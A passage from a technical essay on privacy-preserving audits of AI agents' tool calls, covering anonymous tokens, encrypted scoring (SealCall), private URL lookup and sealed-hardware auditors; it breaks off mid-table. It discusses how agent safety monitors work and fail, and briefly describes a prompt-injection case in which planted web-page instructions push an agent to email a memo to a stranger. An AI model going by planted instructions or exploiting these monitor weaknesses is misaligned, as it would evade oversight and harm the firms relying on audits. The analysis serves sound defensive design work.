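*The Privacy Pass Architecture* (Davidson, Iyengar and Wood, 2024) describes how to build a service on such tokens. Privacy Pass is a set of Internet Engineering Task Force documents, originally meant to help websites limit abusive traffic from anonymity networks such as Tor. The architecture document also mentions using the tokens to prove that someone subscribes to an Oblivious HTTP service, which is very close to what the law firm needs.

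*Anonymous credentials* describes a version in which the firm generates a long random serial number, and the blind signature covers this number, the token type and any agreed metadata. When the firm spends the token, the auditor checks the signature, looks up the serial number in a database of spent tokens, and rejects the request if the number is already there. The firm can buy tokens long before it needs them, so using one adds only a signature check and a lookup to a live audit.

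Other services already sell access this way. Chainbound's *Private API Credits* explains that Kagi, a subscription search engine, uses Privacy Pass so that paying users can search without linking their searches to their accounts. The merger search in the running example is a similar request. At PrivateStorage, a customer pays by card and gets a voucher, which the software exchanges for a batch of blinded tokens. The company can't connect the voucher to the tokens, according to Least Authority's *How Anonymous Credentials Redefine Digital Access*.

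*Double-Blind Verification* (2026), from the identity-checking company Persona, goes further and describes an age-checking system that can bill for each check without learning which business obtained the credential behind it. An auditor would have to do the same with law firms. However, this is Persona's own account, and an age check contains much less revealing text than an email to a client.

Some auditors might prefer to sell subscriptions. Mao, Liao and Liu (2024) designed a subscription scheme for language models using partially blind signatures, in which the signer sees only part of the message. The visible part can set a subscription period, during which the user may send unlimited requests. Their second scheme covers services that charge by use.

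The auditor still has to find out who is entitled to tokens, a job Davidson and colleagues give to a separate role, the attester. If one company is attester, issuer and receiver, they advise against identifying users by their accounts, because the company could link the purchase of tokens to their use through timing or other traces. An auditor would probably start with this arrangement, though, because it already has a billing department. It would be safer for someone else, such as the law firms' professional association, to take the payments and confirm to the auditor that each token request comes from a paid-up member. The association would know which firms use the auditor but would not see their records.

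Tokens limit how many requests a customer can make, but not what those requests contain. Someone testing malicious URLs on the auditor has to pay for every attempt, and the auditor can cap token sales per account. But it cannot tell which account an abusive request came from, so it cannot stop selling to that customer. Customers can also pass tokens to each other. Davidson and colleagues call it a hoarding attack when many people collect tokens for one person to spend. This may not matter to an auditor that charges for every token, but it would matter to one that accepts only vetted law firms.

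### One credential for many requests

A firm whose agents make 10,000 requests needs 10,000 single-use tokens, but the issuer has to sign a multi-show credential only once. Each time the holder uses the credential, it gives a zero-knowledge proof, which shows that it has a valid signature without revealing the signature or anything else. OONI's *Probe Security Without Identification* traces such credentials to work by Jan Camenisch and Anna Lysyanskaya in 2002. OONI, which measures internet censorship with software on volunteers' devices, needs them because the devices upload results continuously.

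An auditor would want to limit how many times a firm can use its credential, and it can if the credential contains a secret and each use has a number *i*. The firm computes a serial number from the secret and *i*, then proves in zero knowledge that it computed the serial number correctly and that *i* is between 1 and, say, 10,000. The serial numbers look unrelated, but reusing an *i* produces the same serial number, so the auditor refuses the second request.

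A credential can keep track of a balance, and this flexible accounting is a better reason to choose it than saving storage. An RSA signature with a 2,048-bit key takes 256 bytes, so 10,000 of them fit in under 3 megabytes. In tests by Kastner and colleagues, a typical laptop needed up to half a second to generate a signature under their new method, which includes a zero-knowledge proof, and up to a tenth of a second to verify one. If every audit needed a fresh proof at that speed, the proof could take half of Microsoft's one second, unless the firm prepared it in advance.

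### A deposit with a penalty for cheating

*ZK API Usage Credits*, a 2026 proposal by Crapis and Buterin on a research forum for the Ethereum blockchain, combines such a balance with penalties. They had in mind people who pay for a hosted language model, but the scheme would also suit other paid requests.

The firm generates a secret *k* and deposits an amount *D* in a smart contract, a program on the blockchain that holds money and pays it out by fixed rules. The contract adds a hash of *k* to a public list of depositors. For request number *i*, counting from 0, the firm proves in zero knowledge that it is on the list and that

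(*i* + 1) · *C*<sub>max</sub> ≤ *D* + *R*,

where *C*<sub>max</sub> is the most that one request can cost and *R* is the sum of the refunds it has received. Suppose the firm deposits $100, the maximum price is $1, and each audit turns out to cost 20 cents. The deposit covers 100 requests at first. After each one, the auditor signs a refund of 80 cents, and with all the refunds counted, the deposit lasts for nearly 500. The auditor learns that the firm has enough credit, but not how much.

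Each request also carries a nullifier, which the firm computes from *k* and *i* and which works like the serial number of a token. The firm also sends a point on the line *y* = *k* + *ax*, where *x* is a hash of the request and *a* is a hash of *k* and *i*. Suppose *k* is 12 and *a* is 5. The request for the docket record hashes to *x* = 3, so the firm sends *y* = 27. Many lines pass through the point (3, 27), so the auditor cannot find *k*. If the firm uses the same *i* for the merger search, which hashes to *x* = 7, it must also send *y* = 47. The auditor recognises the repeated nullifier, computes the slope as (47 − 27)/(7 − 3) = 5, and gets *k* = 27 − 5 × 3 = 12. Anyone who knows *k* can claim the deposit.

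The firm can safely resend a record if a relay drops it, because the same record produces the same point. But two of the firm's machines might accidentally use the same number for different records, or one might go back to an old number after someone restores a backup. The firm would then lose its deposit. It would also lose its past anonymity, because the auditor could use *k* to compute the nullifier of every earlier request and pick out all of the firm's records.

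This penalty seems too harsh for an audit. The auditor checks each nullifier before it replies, so it could refuse the second request. A forum commenter also argued that spam is less of a concern for a service that charges for every request, and that penalties make more sense for free services.

Crapis and Buterin add a second deposit, which the service can destroy if a user breaks the rules, for example by asking a model how to build a weapon. The service can't keep the deposit, so it gains nothing from false accusations, and it has to record each penalty publicly. They don't explain how the contract finds the right deposit from a nullifier that is meant to be untraceable. The penalty also suits audits poorly, because it would punish a customer for using the service as intended. If someone plants instructions in a web page and a law firm's agent tries to email a memo to a stranger, the firm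 wants the auditor to see that request and block it.

A commenter who had worked as an engineer at Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models, objected to the refunds because their amounts vary with the length of the model's answers and, together with response times, could help a service group requests by user. Anonymous users also can't dispute a refund that is too small without identifying themselves. The commenter suggested a few fixed price classes with no refunds, and estimated that users would pay 20–40% more for capacity they didn't use. An auditor could easily use fixed prices, since its answer is always one word and the length of the record is known in advance.

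The same commenter found a flaw in a later version that kept the refund total encrypted. The service saw the same encrypted total when it added a refund and again at the user's next request, so it could link each user's requests to one another. Crapis then changed the design so the encrypted value looks different each time. One developer has built a demonstration, but it leaves out the anonymous rate limits and penalties. If an auditor charges a flat price, single-use tokens would do nearly everything this scheme does, and much less could go wrong.

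### Open Anonymity's tickets for AI chats

The Open Anonymity Project's *oa-chat* is a working program that uses blind signatures with AI models. It offers what the project calls unlinkable inference, which means the company running the model can read a prompt but cannot tell who sent it or connect it with the same person's other sessions. According to the project's *Open Anonymity Station*, the user obtains blind-signed tickets and gives some of them to a server called a station. The station checks the tickets without learning who the user is, then hands over a short-lived API key from OpenRouter, a service that provides access to many companies' models. The user's software uses this key to send prompts directly to the model service.

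The tickets and the key do not hide the user's network address, so the user also needs a proxy. An outline of Augmented Mind's *The Privacy Layer of Personal Intelligence with Ken Liu*, an interview with the project's founder, lists secure inference proxies and blind signatures as parts of the design.

The Open Anonymity project assumes that model providers will try to identify users, and says that users don't have to trust any component it runs. No component holds the user's identity, so a corrupt operator couldn't reveal it. A verifier running in sealed hardware checks that stations own the keys they hand out and keep the required privacy settings. But Pham, Sheils and colleagues (2026), in *Can Prompt Anonymity Protect Your Identity From LLM Providers?*, class Open Anonymity with other anonymizing proxies and say that users must trust these services, without formal proof, not to mishandle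 their prompts.

The project does not claim to hide the prompts. In the Brave podcast interview *Your AI Chats Aren’t Private (And How “Unlinkable Inference” Can Help)*, Ken Liu distinguishes two kinds of sensitive prompt. Removing the account details protects someone who asks where to get antidepressants in Palo Alto, because many people might ask that. Someone who pastes in a CV before an hour of therapy has identified themselves. The law firm's docket fetch is closer to the first kind, and its signed email to the second. The project also has a text scrubber to address what prompts reveal by themselves.

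Open Anonymity protects users from the company that runs the model, so using it with an auditor would require several changes. First, the law firm would need a separate token for each request. The chat program uses one key per session, which lets the provider link all the requests in that session. A person may not mind this in a single conversation, but if the firm used one key for the whole Northgate task, the auditor could use the document link to identify the firm's other requests too.

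Tokens for the audit, like a relay, would not hide the firm from the developer. The developer could still work out which records are the firm's by sharing its logs with the auditor. The firm could pay anonymously for both the model and the audits, but it would need separate credentials for each so that neither the developer nor the auditor could recognise a token the other had seen.

Unlike a person, who can reread a prompt before sending it, an agent may send hundreds of requests that nobody at the firm has read.

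### How a token can still identify its holder

A blind signature hides a firm only among the others that could hold the same kind of token. Davidson and colleagues compare an anonymity set of two with one of 2<sup>32</sup>, about 4.3 billion. The cryptography works equally well in both, but in the smaller one a guess is right half the time. Suppose the auditor replaces its signing key every month and only 40 of its 200 firms buy tokens under the current key. A token then narrows the sender to those 40 before the auditor reads any of the record. Replacing the key less often would let more firms buy tokens under the same key, but anyone who stole it could forge tokens for longer.

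The number of tokens each firm buys also affects anonymity. If one large firm buys 50,000 tokens and the other 199 buy 500 each, the large firm holds about a third of all the tokens. If all the firms spend their tokens at a similar rate, the auditor could guess the large firm for every request and be right about a third of the time.

Buying a token just before spending it can reveal who sent a request. Some Privacy Pass services send the client a fresh challenge and accept only tokens issued in response to it. The sender must then be one of the clients that requested a token between the challenge and the reply. Late in the evening, only one law firm may have done so. Buying tokens in advance avoids this, but a firm that runs out, buys more at 21:58 and resumes its requests at 22:00 still gives the auditor a strong hint of its identity. The firms could instead all buy batches of the same size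 on the same day each month, though some tokens would go unused.

Any label on a token divides the token's holders into groups. Three yes-or-no labels reduce 200 candidates to 25 if each splits the firms evenly, but real labels rarely do. If only one firm has bought the auditor's package for merger work, the token type alone identifies it. An expiry date like the one in the scheme by Mao and colleagues could also identify a firm if it were exact to the day and only one firm's subscription ended that day. All subscriptions should therefore end on a few shared dates. OONI has the same problem with facts such as how long a volunteer's device has been taking part, and requires credentials that can confirm these facts without revealing the exact values.

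An auditor can also secretly label one firm's tokens by signing them with a different key from the one it uses for other firms, much as a dishonest gateway can hand out different encryption keys. In both cases, the remedy is for the firms to check that they all received the same key.

That check doesn't help if the firm's own software secretly reveals who the firm is. *Privacy Pass is Anamorphic* proves that the three most prominent versions of Privacy Pass allow hidden messages inside values that look normal. For example, the software could encrypt the firm's name and use the result as the "random" serial number, and anyone with the right key could then read the name. An inspector could not detect this even with all the private keys used in the protocol. Security companies often supply the software that connects customers to their services, so a law firm that wants to stay anonymous should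 get its token software from someone other than the auditor, preferably with source code that others can inspect.

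## The case for scoring requests under encryption

Even if the law firm sends its client email through a relay and pays with an anonymous token, the auditor still reads "A. Reyes, The Firm LLP" at the bottom of the message. Some researchers would therefore keep the text from the auditor. The firm needs the auditor's knowledge of attacks, and these researchers argue that the auditor can supply it without reading the firm's requests. The firm turns a request into numbers and encrypts them, the auditor compares the encrypted numbers with known dangerous cases, and only the firm can decrypt the result.

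Luo and colleagues built SealCall to try scoring agents' tool calls under encryption, so we have direct evidence about this approach, which we lacked for relays and tokens.

### Arithmetic on encrypted numbers

Homomorphic encryption lets someone add and multiply encrypted numbers without being able to decrypt them. The results are also encrypted, and only the holder of the secret key can read them. An audit mostly needs to compute dot products. A dot product multiplies two lists of numbers entry by entry and adds up the results. The dot product of (3, 5) and (2, 4) is 3 × 2 + 5 × 4 = 26.

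A toy scheme shows how an auditor could compute this without seeing the 3 or the 5. The firm keeps the number 1,009 secret. It encrypts a small number by adding a random multiple of 1,009, and decrypts by dividing by 1,009 and keeping the remainder.

1. The firm encrypts 3 as 3 + 17 × 1,009 = 17,156 and 5 as 5 + 42 × 1,009 = 42,383, and sends both to the auditor.
2. The auditor, whose own numbers are 2 and 4, computes 2 × 17,156 + 4 × 42,383 = 203,844 and returns it.
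3. The firm divides 203,844 by 1,009 and gets a remainder of 26.

This works because a multiple of 1,009 stays a multiple of 1,009 whatever the auditor multiplies it by, so it disappears when the firm takes the remainder. The true answer has to be smaller than 1,009. The method would also work if the auditor's 2 and 4 were encrypted, because multiplying two encrypted numbers only adds more multiples of 1,009.

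The toy scheme is not secure, because anyone who obtained a few encryptions of zero could find 1,009 as their common factor. Real schemes prevent this by adding a small random error to every encrypted number, and they have to keep the errors from growing large enough to spoil the answer. SealCall uses a scheme called CKKS, which does approximate arithmetic, so its results are very slightly off. In CKKS, a public key encrypts, a secret key decrypts, and an evaluation key lets a server calculate with encrypted numbers. The auditor gets the public key and the evaluation key.

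### From a tool call to a verdict

SealCall divides the work among three domains. The agent runs in one, a trusted program called the controller runs in another under the customer's control, and the auditor's server is the third. In our example, the agent and the controller would both run on the law firm's computers. The controller prepares and encrypts the numbers, the server calculates with the encrypted numbers, and the controller decrypts the result and acts on it.

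When the agent is about to send the client email, the controller keeps the lawyer's task and the complete tool call, then searches the results of earlier calls for the new call's arguments, such as `counsel@northgate.example`. It keeps a few of the matches, with up to 96 characters on either side, and labels each with its source, because an address the lawyer typed carries more authority than one from a web page. In Luo and colleagues' data, this selection cut the text to 21.6% of its original length.

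A small language model then converts the text into an embedding, a list of numbers that is similar for texts with similar meanings. The controller adds other features, such as the tool's name and whether each argument appears in the task, the history, both or neither. A learned formula condenses all of this into a vector *z* of 128 or 256 numbers:

*z* = (*Wx* + *b*) / ‖*Wx* + *b*‖

Here *x* is the combined list after rescaling, and *W* and *b* are learned from labelled examples. The division gives *z* a length of 1. The dot product of two such vectors measures how similar they are, since it is 1 when they point in the same direction and falls as the angle between them grows.

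The controller encrypts *z* and sends it to the server, which holds encrypted vectors *p*<sub>1</sub> to *p*<sub>*K*</sub>, each made from a real unsafe tool call. The server computes the dot product of *z* with every one of them and returns the encrypted results. The controller decrypts them and takes the largest:

*s* = max<sub>*j*</sub> (*z* · *p*<sub>*j*</sub>)

The controller blocks the call if *s* is at least *τ*, a threshold chosen with labelled examples. For example, if *z* were (0.6, 0.8) and the unsafe cases were (0.8, 0.6) and (1, 0), the similarities would be 0.96 and 0.6. With a threshold of 0.9, the controller would block the email because it closely resembles the first case.

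An approval has to apply to one particular call, or the agent could get approval for a harmless email and send a different one. Before requesting the audit, the controller saves an exact copy of the call along with a one-time number and the expected state of the agent's work. It releases only the saved copy, and only if an approval arrives in time and everything still matches. If the result is late or unusable, the call stays blocked, whereas Microsoft's default would let it through. The controller passed all 36 tests that Luo and colleagues ran on this mechanism, including tests with replayed approvals and altered calls.

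They also prove when the small errors of CKKS cannot change a verdict. Suppose every decrypted similarity is within *ε* of its true value. None of them can then exceed *s* + *ε*, and the one that belongs to the closest unsafe case is at least *s* − *ε*, so the largest decrypted value is within *ε* of *s*. The verdict is therefore the same as without encryption whenever

|*s* − *τ*| > *ε*.

In the example, *s* is 0.06 above the threshold. For the version of SealCall's scorer that packs its results into a compact response, the largest measured error was about 0.0000015, so only a call that scored almost exactly at the threshold could get the wrong verdict. Encryption never changed a decision across 760 measurements, which also covered three other scoring methods.

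### How well it recognises unsafe calls

Luo and colleagues tested SealCall on 1,252 tool calls that other researchers had labelled safe or unsafe. The calls came from recorded runs of two public benchmarks. AgentHarm tests whether agents carry out harmful requests, and AgentDojo tests whether they obey instructions that an attacker has planted in their data.

The main measure is the F1 score, which combines the share of unsafe calls that a system catches with the share of its alarms that are correct. A perfect system scores 1. SealCall averaged 0.840 and wrongly blocked 11.2% of safe calls. With a threshold meant to limit false alarms to 10% of safe calls, it blocked 15.3% of them and caught 82.3% of unsafe calls. A law firm whose agents make hundreds of harmless requests a day would get dozens of false alarms.

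Logistic regression, a simpler method that multiplies each input by a learned weight and adds up the results, did better than SealCall, scoring 0.913 on the same calls. It also needs only a dot product from the server, and in the timing test it took 0.043 seconds under encryption, compared with 0.176 for SealCall. SealCall's advantage is that the firm can see which known unsafe case its call resembled. This helps a person review an alarm, but it seems a weak reason to accept more errors.

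These scores may also be a poor measure of how well either method uses context. A logistic regression based on tool names scored 0.846 at the setting where SealCall scored 0.812. If tool names predict the labels that well, a scorer can do well on these benchmarks without any information about what the user authorised. A firm could send an auditor bare tool names with little loss of privacy, so the case for encryption depends on decisions that need the rest of the record.

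SealCall performs poorly when the right decision depends on what the agent is authorised to do. Luo and colleagues wrote 80 scenarios in which the tool call and history stayed the same but the authorisation changed, such as who may receive a message or for what purpose. Each scenario had a safe and an unsafe version, each worded two ways, which made four decisions per scenario. SealCall did not get all four right in any scenario, while random guessing would do so in about five of the 80.

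SealCall probably did worse than chance because the safe and unsafe versions produce nearly the same vector, so they usually get the same verdict. In the law firm's case, the lawyer might say "send the note to Northgate's counsel" or "draft the note to Northgate's counsel, but don't send it until I approve". The agent could propose the same email after either instruction, and SealCall would probably give both the same verdict. It did better when only the wording changed. On 100 tasks that an AI model reworded twice, with the meaning intended to stay the same, it judged all three versions correctly 77.6% of the time.

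The same vectors would get the same verdicts without encryption, so encryption did not cause these failures. The logistic regressions tested also failed in all 80 scenarios, although a simple program written for the scenarios' fixed sentence patterns got every decision right. The text therefore contained the necessary facts, but the scorers missed them. Language models that read the text directly may do better. On 416 of the benchmark calls, the language model StepGuard-4B scored 0.882 against SealCall's 0.837, though its training data may have included some of those tasks.

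### Whether the firm could do the scoring itself

Scoring one call took 0.176 seconds on average, with 16 unsafe cases and vectors of 256 numbers, on a single thread of a recent Intel processor. Including preparation, the average was 0.663 seconds, and 5% of calls took about 1.16 seconds or longer. Most of the time went into computing the embedding, before any encryption. These times exclude network transfer. Each query requires sending about 0.33 megabytes and receiving 0.13. The average call would meet Microsoft's one-second limit if the network were fast, but the slowest calls would not. A firm that runs its own controller could allow more time.

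Once the controller has the vector, comparing it with the unsafe cases takes about 19 microseconds without encryption, some 9,000 times faster than with it. The auditor could send the firm its 16 unsafe vectors, about 16 kilobytes in total, and the firm could score its own calls without revealing anything to anyone.

Luo and colleagues reply that customers are paying for knowledge that a specialist maintains. But the specialist could send updates, as antivirus companies do. Secrecy doesn't justify keeping the vectors on the server either, because SealCall does not hide them from the customer. A customer that submits the vector (1, 0, 0, …) gets back the first coordinate of every unsafe case, and 256 such queries, one for each coordinate, reveal all the vectors. SealCall's designers accept this because they trust the controller, and they say that protecting the auditor's data from customers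 would require a protocol that returns less information.

For SealCall as tested, local scoring looks better than encrypted scoring on both privacy and cost. Encryption becomes worthwhile when the auditor's knowledge is too large to send, changes too quickly, or is too valuable to give away. Knowledge that is too valuable to give away also requires the more restrictive protocol.

### Looking up a URL in secret

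Lists of dangerous web addresses can be large and change quickly. The firm could check the docket page against such a list using private information retrieval (PIR), which fetches a record from a server's database without revealing which record. The simplest form of PIR is to download the whole database, but Swift Package Registry's *Swift Homomorphic Encryption* points out that this is feasible only for small databases.

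Kim (2026), in *High-Throughput Private Information Retrieval with on-CPU Accelerators*, explains a more economical method with a database of four records. Suppose the records are the numbers 12, 40, 7 and 31, and the firm wants the second. It encrypts each entry of the list (0, 1, 0, 0) and sends the result. The server multiplies each record by the matching encrypted entry and adds up the products:

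0 × 12 + 1 × 40 + 0 × 7 + 0 × 31 = 40

The server gets only an encrypted 40, which the firm decrypts. The calculation is another dot product. The server cannot distinguish the encrypted 1 from the encrypted zeros. It has to process every record for every query, because being able to skip one would reveal that the firm had not asked for it.

For the docket page, the firm's software would hash the URL to find which part of the list could contain it, fetch that part privately and look for the URL there. Google's Safe Browsing server, by contrast, sees the first four bytes of the hash. Kim tested private checks against a list of 1.1 million phishing links and domains, divided into 16,384 parts of 4 kilobytes each. Every check makes six requests, to cover the link, its host and its parent domains. If an address needs fewer, the check adds random requests to reach six, so that the count reveals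 nothing.

Reading the whole database for every query used to make PIR slow. In *Robust, privacy-preserving, transparent, and auditable on-device blocklisting* (2023), a lookup took 183 milliseconds of server time for about 54,000 entries and 1.4 seconds for about 870,000, which would already exceed Microsoft's limit. Kim's system, AltoPIR, answers a query on a 1-gigabyte database in 13.9 milliseconds on a 16-core processor. The client sends 192 kilobytes and receives 112. The server can answer 2,013 queries per second by combining queries from many clients in each pass over the database. The two systems use different methods and machines, and AltoPIR needs a processor with a built-in matrix-multiplication unit, but a private URL lookup can now be fast enough for a live audit.

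The phishing list in this test takes up only 64 megabytes, so a law firm could easily download it. The reason to query a server instead, as in Safe Browsing, is to get fresh information. But whenever the database changes, AltoPIR's server has to recompute some stored data, which takes about as much work for one changed record as for many. Kim therefore recommends grouping updates, which delays new entries.

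Since version 26, iOS and macOS have used PIR to let makers of parental controls, school filters and similar apps block individual web addresses without seeing which ones people open. As Apple's *Filter and tunnel network traffic with NetworkExtension* explains, the device first checks each URL against a Bloom filter, a compact table built from the list of blocked addresses. If the filter finds no match, the URL is certainly not on the list, and the page loads at once. A match may be a false alarm, so the device checks it by sending a PIR query to the app maker's server, which learns neither the URL nor the answer.

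text/plain's *First Look* (2025), a blog post on the feature, compares the general design to Safe Browsing. Outside companies have begun to use it. In Manual do Usuário's *Wipr 2 expands Safari ad blocking to all other apps*, the developer of an ad blocker says that hers is the first app to do so.

Each query reveals to the server that some device opened an address that might be on the list. How much this reveals depends on how often the Bloom filter gives false alarms. If it wrongly matches 1% of harmless addresses and only one address in 10,000 is on the list, about 99% of queries will concern harmless pages. A filter with fewer false alarms would trigger fewer queries, but each would be more likely to concern a listed address.

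An auditor could use PIR to check the docket page and the domain of an email's recipient. PIR wouldn't work for the merger search or the body of the email, because the auditor has no list of dangerous sentences to look them up in. Those need a scorer like SealCall's, despite its current weaknesses.

### Encrypted requests still have a sender

SealCall would hide the text of all four of the law firm's requests, but not who sends them. The auditor's server still receives the firm's network address. Luo and colleagues state that the timing of requests and the layout of the encrypted data also remain visible.

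A relay and anonymous tokens could hide the firm's address and account, but its encryption keys would still link its requests. The SealCall paper doesn't discuss this, but it seems to follow from the design. The server needs the firm's evaluation key and holds the unsafe cases encrypted under the firm's public key. To score a query, it has to know which set of encrypted cases to use, so every request from the firm points to the same set. If the auditor connects one of those requests with the firm, it can attribute all of them. It still couldn't read any, but it could see, for example, that the firm's agents were unusually busy the night before a merger announcement.

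The firm could avoid this by using new keys for every request. In SealCall, someone would have to encrypt the unsafe cases again for each request, which takes only 0.066 seconds for 16 cases but produces 5.3 megabytes of data. The server would also need a new evaluation key. PIR handles new keys better. AltoPIR's clients send their keys with each query, and the 192 kilobytes already include them. Every query in Kim's tests used new keys.

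Apple's products combine encryption with ways of hiding the sender. Its URL filter uses Privacy Pass tokens and Oblivious HTTP, with Apple running the relay and the app maker running the gateway. Apple's *Understanding how Live Caller ID Lookup preserves privacy* describes similar protections for a service that checks incoming calls against lists of known spam numbers.

A feature of Apple's Photos app comes closer to SealCall because it compares encrypted vectors instead of looking for exact matches. The phone turns part of a photo into a vector, encrypts it and has a server compare it with a database of landmarks. Comparing it with every landmark would take too much computing, so the server searches only the part of the database that the phone specifies. Apple notes that this choice could reveal something sensitive about the photo. The phone therefore also sends fake queries, and a relay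 run by another company hides the phone's network address.

*Wally* (Asi, Boemer and colleagues, 2024), the paper behind this design, shows that it increases throughput when there are many users. With batches of 500,000 queries on a database of 3.2 million entries, the system handled 7 to 29 times as many queries per second as Tiptoe, an earlier system that searches the whole database every time. With fewer users, each has to send more fake queries to get the same protection. Clients also send their queries at random times within a fixed period, which suits a photo library but not an agent waiting to send an email. An auditor with 200 law firms would be better off comparing each request with its whole collection, as SealCall does, as long as the collection stays small.

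### Only the customer learns the verdict

SealCall's server returns an encrypted score, and the auditor never learns whether the controller blocked the call. This is enough if the law firm wants protection from its own agent's mistakes, because the firm has good reason to act on the score. But if the agent tries to attack someone else's server, the auditor won't know about the attempt and so cannot warn the victim or tell a regulator. A customer who wanted the attack to succeed could ignore the score. Encrypted scoring of this kind can therefore be used for audits that protect the customer, but not for audits meant to protect the public.

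The auditor also loses much of its ability to compare attacks across customers. It never sees a request or a verdict, so it cannot learn about new attacks from its own service. Customers would have to volunteer examples of blocked calls, or the auditor would have to find examples elsewhere.

The customer has to trust the auditor too. SealCall assumes that the server is semi-honest. A malicious server could return a properly encrypted false score, and the controller would accept it. Preventing this would require proof that the server calculated the score correctly, which SealCall does not provide.

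A server can sometimes enforce a verdict without learning it. Min, Lee and colleagues (2026), in *HE-Guardrail*, study a language model that answers encrypted prompts, where the company running the model wants to withhold harmful answers but can't read the prompts. The server computes an encrypted number *g*, which is 1 for a safe prompt and 0 for a harmful one, and returns

*gY* + (1 − *g*)*R* + noise,

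where *Y* is the model's answer and *R* is a refusal. A user with a safe prompt gets the answer, a user with a harmful one gets the refusal, and the server doesn't know which it sent. The noise is necessary because *g* may come out as 0.01 instead of 0, which would leave a faint trace of the forbidden answer. The encrypted checks agreed with ordinary ones in 99.7% of cases, but running one of them, Llama Guard, as a separate model took about 140 gibibytes of additional graphics memory.

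This works because the server has something the user wants. In the law firm's case, the firm already has the email and the means to send it, so the auditor has nothing to withhold. It would have something to withhold if outside services refused requests without the auditor's signed approval, and if the server could release that approval under encryption in the same way. The agent's attack would then fail, but the auditor still wouldn't know that anyone had tried it.

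## The case for an auditor that runs inside sealed hardware

SealCall kept the law firm's email from the auditor, but its verdict would probably have been the same whether or not the lawyer had approved sending it. A language model that reads the lawyer's instruction alongside the email is more likely to detect whether the lawyer approved it, but it needs both in plain text. Supporters of sealed hardware propose running a program inside it that reads everything and releases only agreed answers. The auditor's staff would never see the email, and the firm could check which program read it.

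Other kinds of audit could work the same way. *Securing deep third-party frontier AI evaluations*, for example, proposes letting outsiders study an AI model's inner workings without exposing the model. But how such a system would work for an anonymous law firm is partly guesswork.

### How the firm can check which program is running

The program runs in a trusted execution environment (TEE). Sealed memory alone wouldn't reassure the law firm, because the auditor could load a program that forwards every email to its sales department. The firm also needs attestation to show which program is running. Jin, Duan and colleagues (2026), in *Proof-of-Guardrail in AI Agents and What (Not) to Trust from It*, describe the basic procedure, and Breckenridge, Fábrega and colleagues (2026), in *πCreds*, also tie an encryption key to the program. For the docket record, it would go like this:

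1. The auditor publishes the program's source code. The firm, or an expert it trusts, reads the code, builds the program and computes its hash. Suppose the hash begins with `9c41` (the values here are invented).
2. The auditor loads the program into the TEE. The hardware computes the same hash, known as the measurement, and records it.
3. The program generates a public and a private key. The private key never leaves the TEE.
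4. The firm's software sends a fresh random number and asks for an attestation. The hardware signs a statement containing the measurement, a fingerprint of the public key and the random number. It signs with a key that the manufacturer built into the chip.
5. The firm's software checks the signature, the measurement, the fingerprint and the random number, which shows that the statement isn't an old one. If everything matches, the software encrypts the docket record with the public key and sends it.

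If the auditor adds one line that copies every email signature to a file, the program's hash changes, perhaps to one beginning with `e07b`. Nobody knows a practical way to change the program and keep the old hash. The hardware signs `e07b`, but the firm's software expected `9c41`, so the record stays at the firm. When Jin and colleagues changed a line in a safety check for agents, the measurement did not match in any of 10 trials. They also altered the attestation 100 times and the agent's response 100 times, and verification caught every change.

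Their safety check took 0.55 seconds on average inside the TEE, compared with 0.42 outside, and producing an attestation took another 0.1. This would usually fit within Microsoft's one second. However, their program sent the text to a model running elsewhere. A law firm could not accept that, so the model would have to run in sealed hardware too. That used to be expensive. In *Attestable Audits* (2025), a prototype that ran AI safety tests in a TEE cost 21.7 times as much as running the model on an ordinary graphics processor. Newer graphics processors have their own sealed mode. Breckenridge and colleagues used it for their prototype and report that it slows many language-model workloads only slightly.

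### What the measurement leaves out

A matching measurement confirms only the inputs that the hardware measured. The security company Trail of Bits audited the WhatsApp system that summarises messages inside TEEs and found several weaknesses, all of which Meta has fixed. In *What we learned about TEE security from auditing WhatsApp's Private Inference* (2026), the company warns that any input the hardware doesn't measure can become a vulnerability. For instance, if the program reads its settings from an unmeasured file, the operator might change the program's behaviour without changing its hash.

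In *Hardware attestation for end-to-end encrypted AI inference*, Bednar found gaps of this kind in Venice, a service that sells private access to AI models. The attestation did not cover the model or the software that served it, and it could not show whether someone had added a key for remote administrator access. Leaving the model out of the attestation would be a serious gap in an audit, because the auditor could replace the model that judges the firm's requests without the firm noticing.

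The amount of software to check is also growing. Intel's older technology, SGX, seals off part of an application, while the newer TDX seals off a whole virtual machine, including an operating system. Tom's Hardware's *Intel to phase out SGX after Xeon Diamond Rapids* reports that Intel will concentrate on TDX, which is easier for cloud companies to use. A law firm would then probably rely on outside experts to check the program.

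### The auditor in a box

The most complete design for such an audit comes from *Auditor-in-a-Box: Tools for Third-Party Auditing*, a 2026 post on the discussion site LessWrong. In this design, two parties who don't trust each other, such as an AI developer and a customer, agree on a plan that lists the inputs, every step of the computation and the outputs. A step can be a short piece of code or a prompt for a named open-weight model, which both sides can download and test. Both sign the plan, and the program in the TEE runs only that plan.

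The design is meant to solve a problem with zero data retention, a contract term under which the developer does not store a customer's inputs and outputs. The term protects the customer, but it means that the developer can only check each query by itself. It can't notice a series of harmless-looking queries that are dangerous together. The post proposes a relaxed version, "ZDR-lite", in which the developer keeps the logs but can't read them:

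1. The customer and the developer sign a plan that says what the developer may look for and what form the answers may take.
2. The program in the TEE generates its keys and publishes the public one with an attestation.
3. The developer encrypts each conversation log with that key and stores only the encrypted copy. (It has, of course, handled the text before encrypting it.)
4. When the developer has a question, the program compares it with the signed plan and refuses any question outside the agreed scope.
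5. If the question is in scope, the program decrypts the logs and the model works out an answer. An output filter then releases only what the plan allows.

The output filter can be a few lines of ordinary code that let through a single bit, a yes or a no. Even if the model goes wrong and outputs an entire email, only one bit leaves in each run.

The second use is a recurring outside audit of an AI company. An evaluator gets access to the company's data and part of its code and decides what to ask, such as whether the company trained a model on certain personal data. The evaluator then turns the question into a program that runs in the box and releases, say, one bit a week. The post mentions METR, an organisation that evaluates AI models, as a precedent for placing an evaluator inside a company.

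The post's publicly released code runs example plans in a real TEE. In one plan, a developer may learn only what share of a user's chats is about work. The public demonstration isn't secure, because anyone can sign in as both parties and see each side's data. The design is meant to withstand people who have a reason to break its guarantees, but no such person has tried yet.

### The law firm's log in the box

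Neither of these uses hides the customer's identity. The two parties know each other from the start, and the TEE protects only what the customer wrote. An anonymous audit would therefore have to change the design. Records from all 200 law firms would go into one pool, through a relay and with anonymous tokens. The firms would also need a shared plan, because a plan signed with a firm's own key would identify that firm. Their professional association could negotiate and sign the shared plan for all of them.

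Inside the sealed hardware, the model can read the lawyer's task, the document link and the signature on the client email. The auditor asks whether any request broke a rule and receives a yes or no answer. The protection this gives the firm depends on which other questions the auditor may ask.

| Question to the box | What a "yes" tells the auditor |
|---|---|
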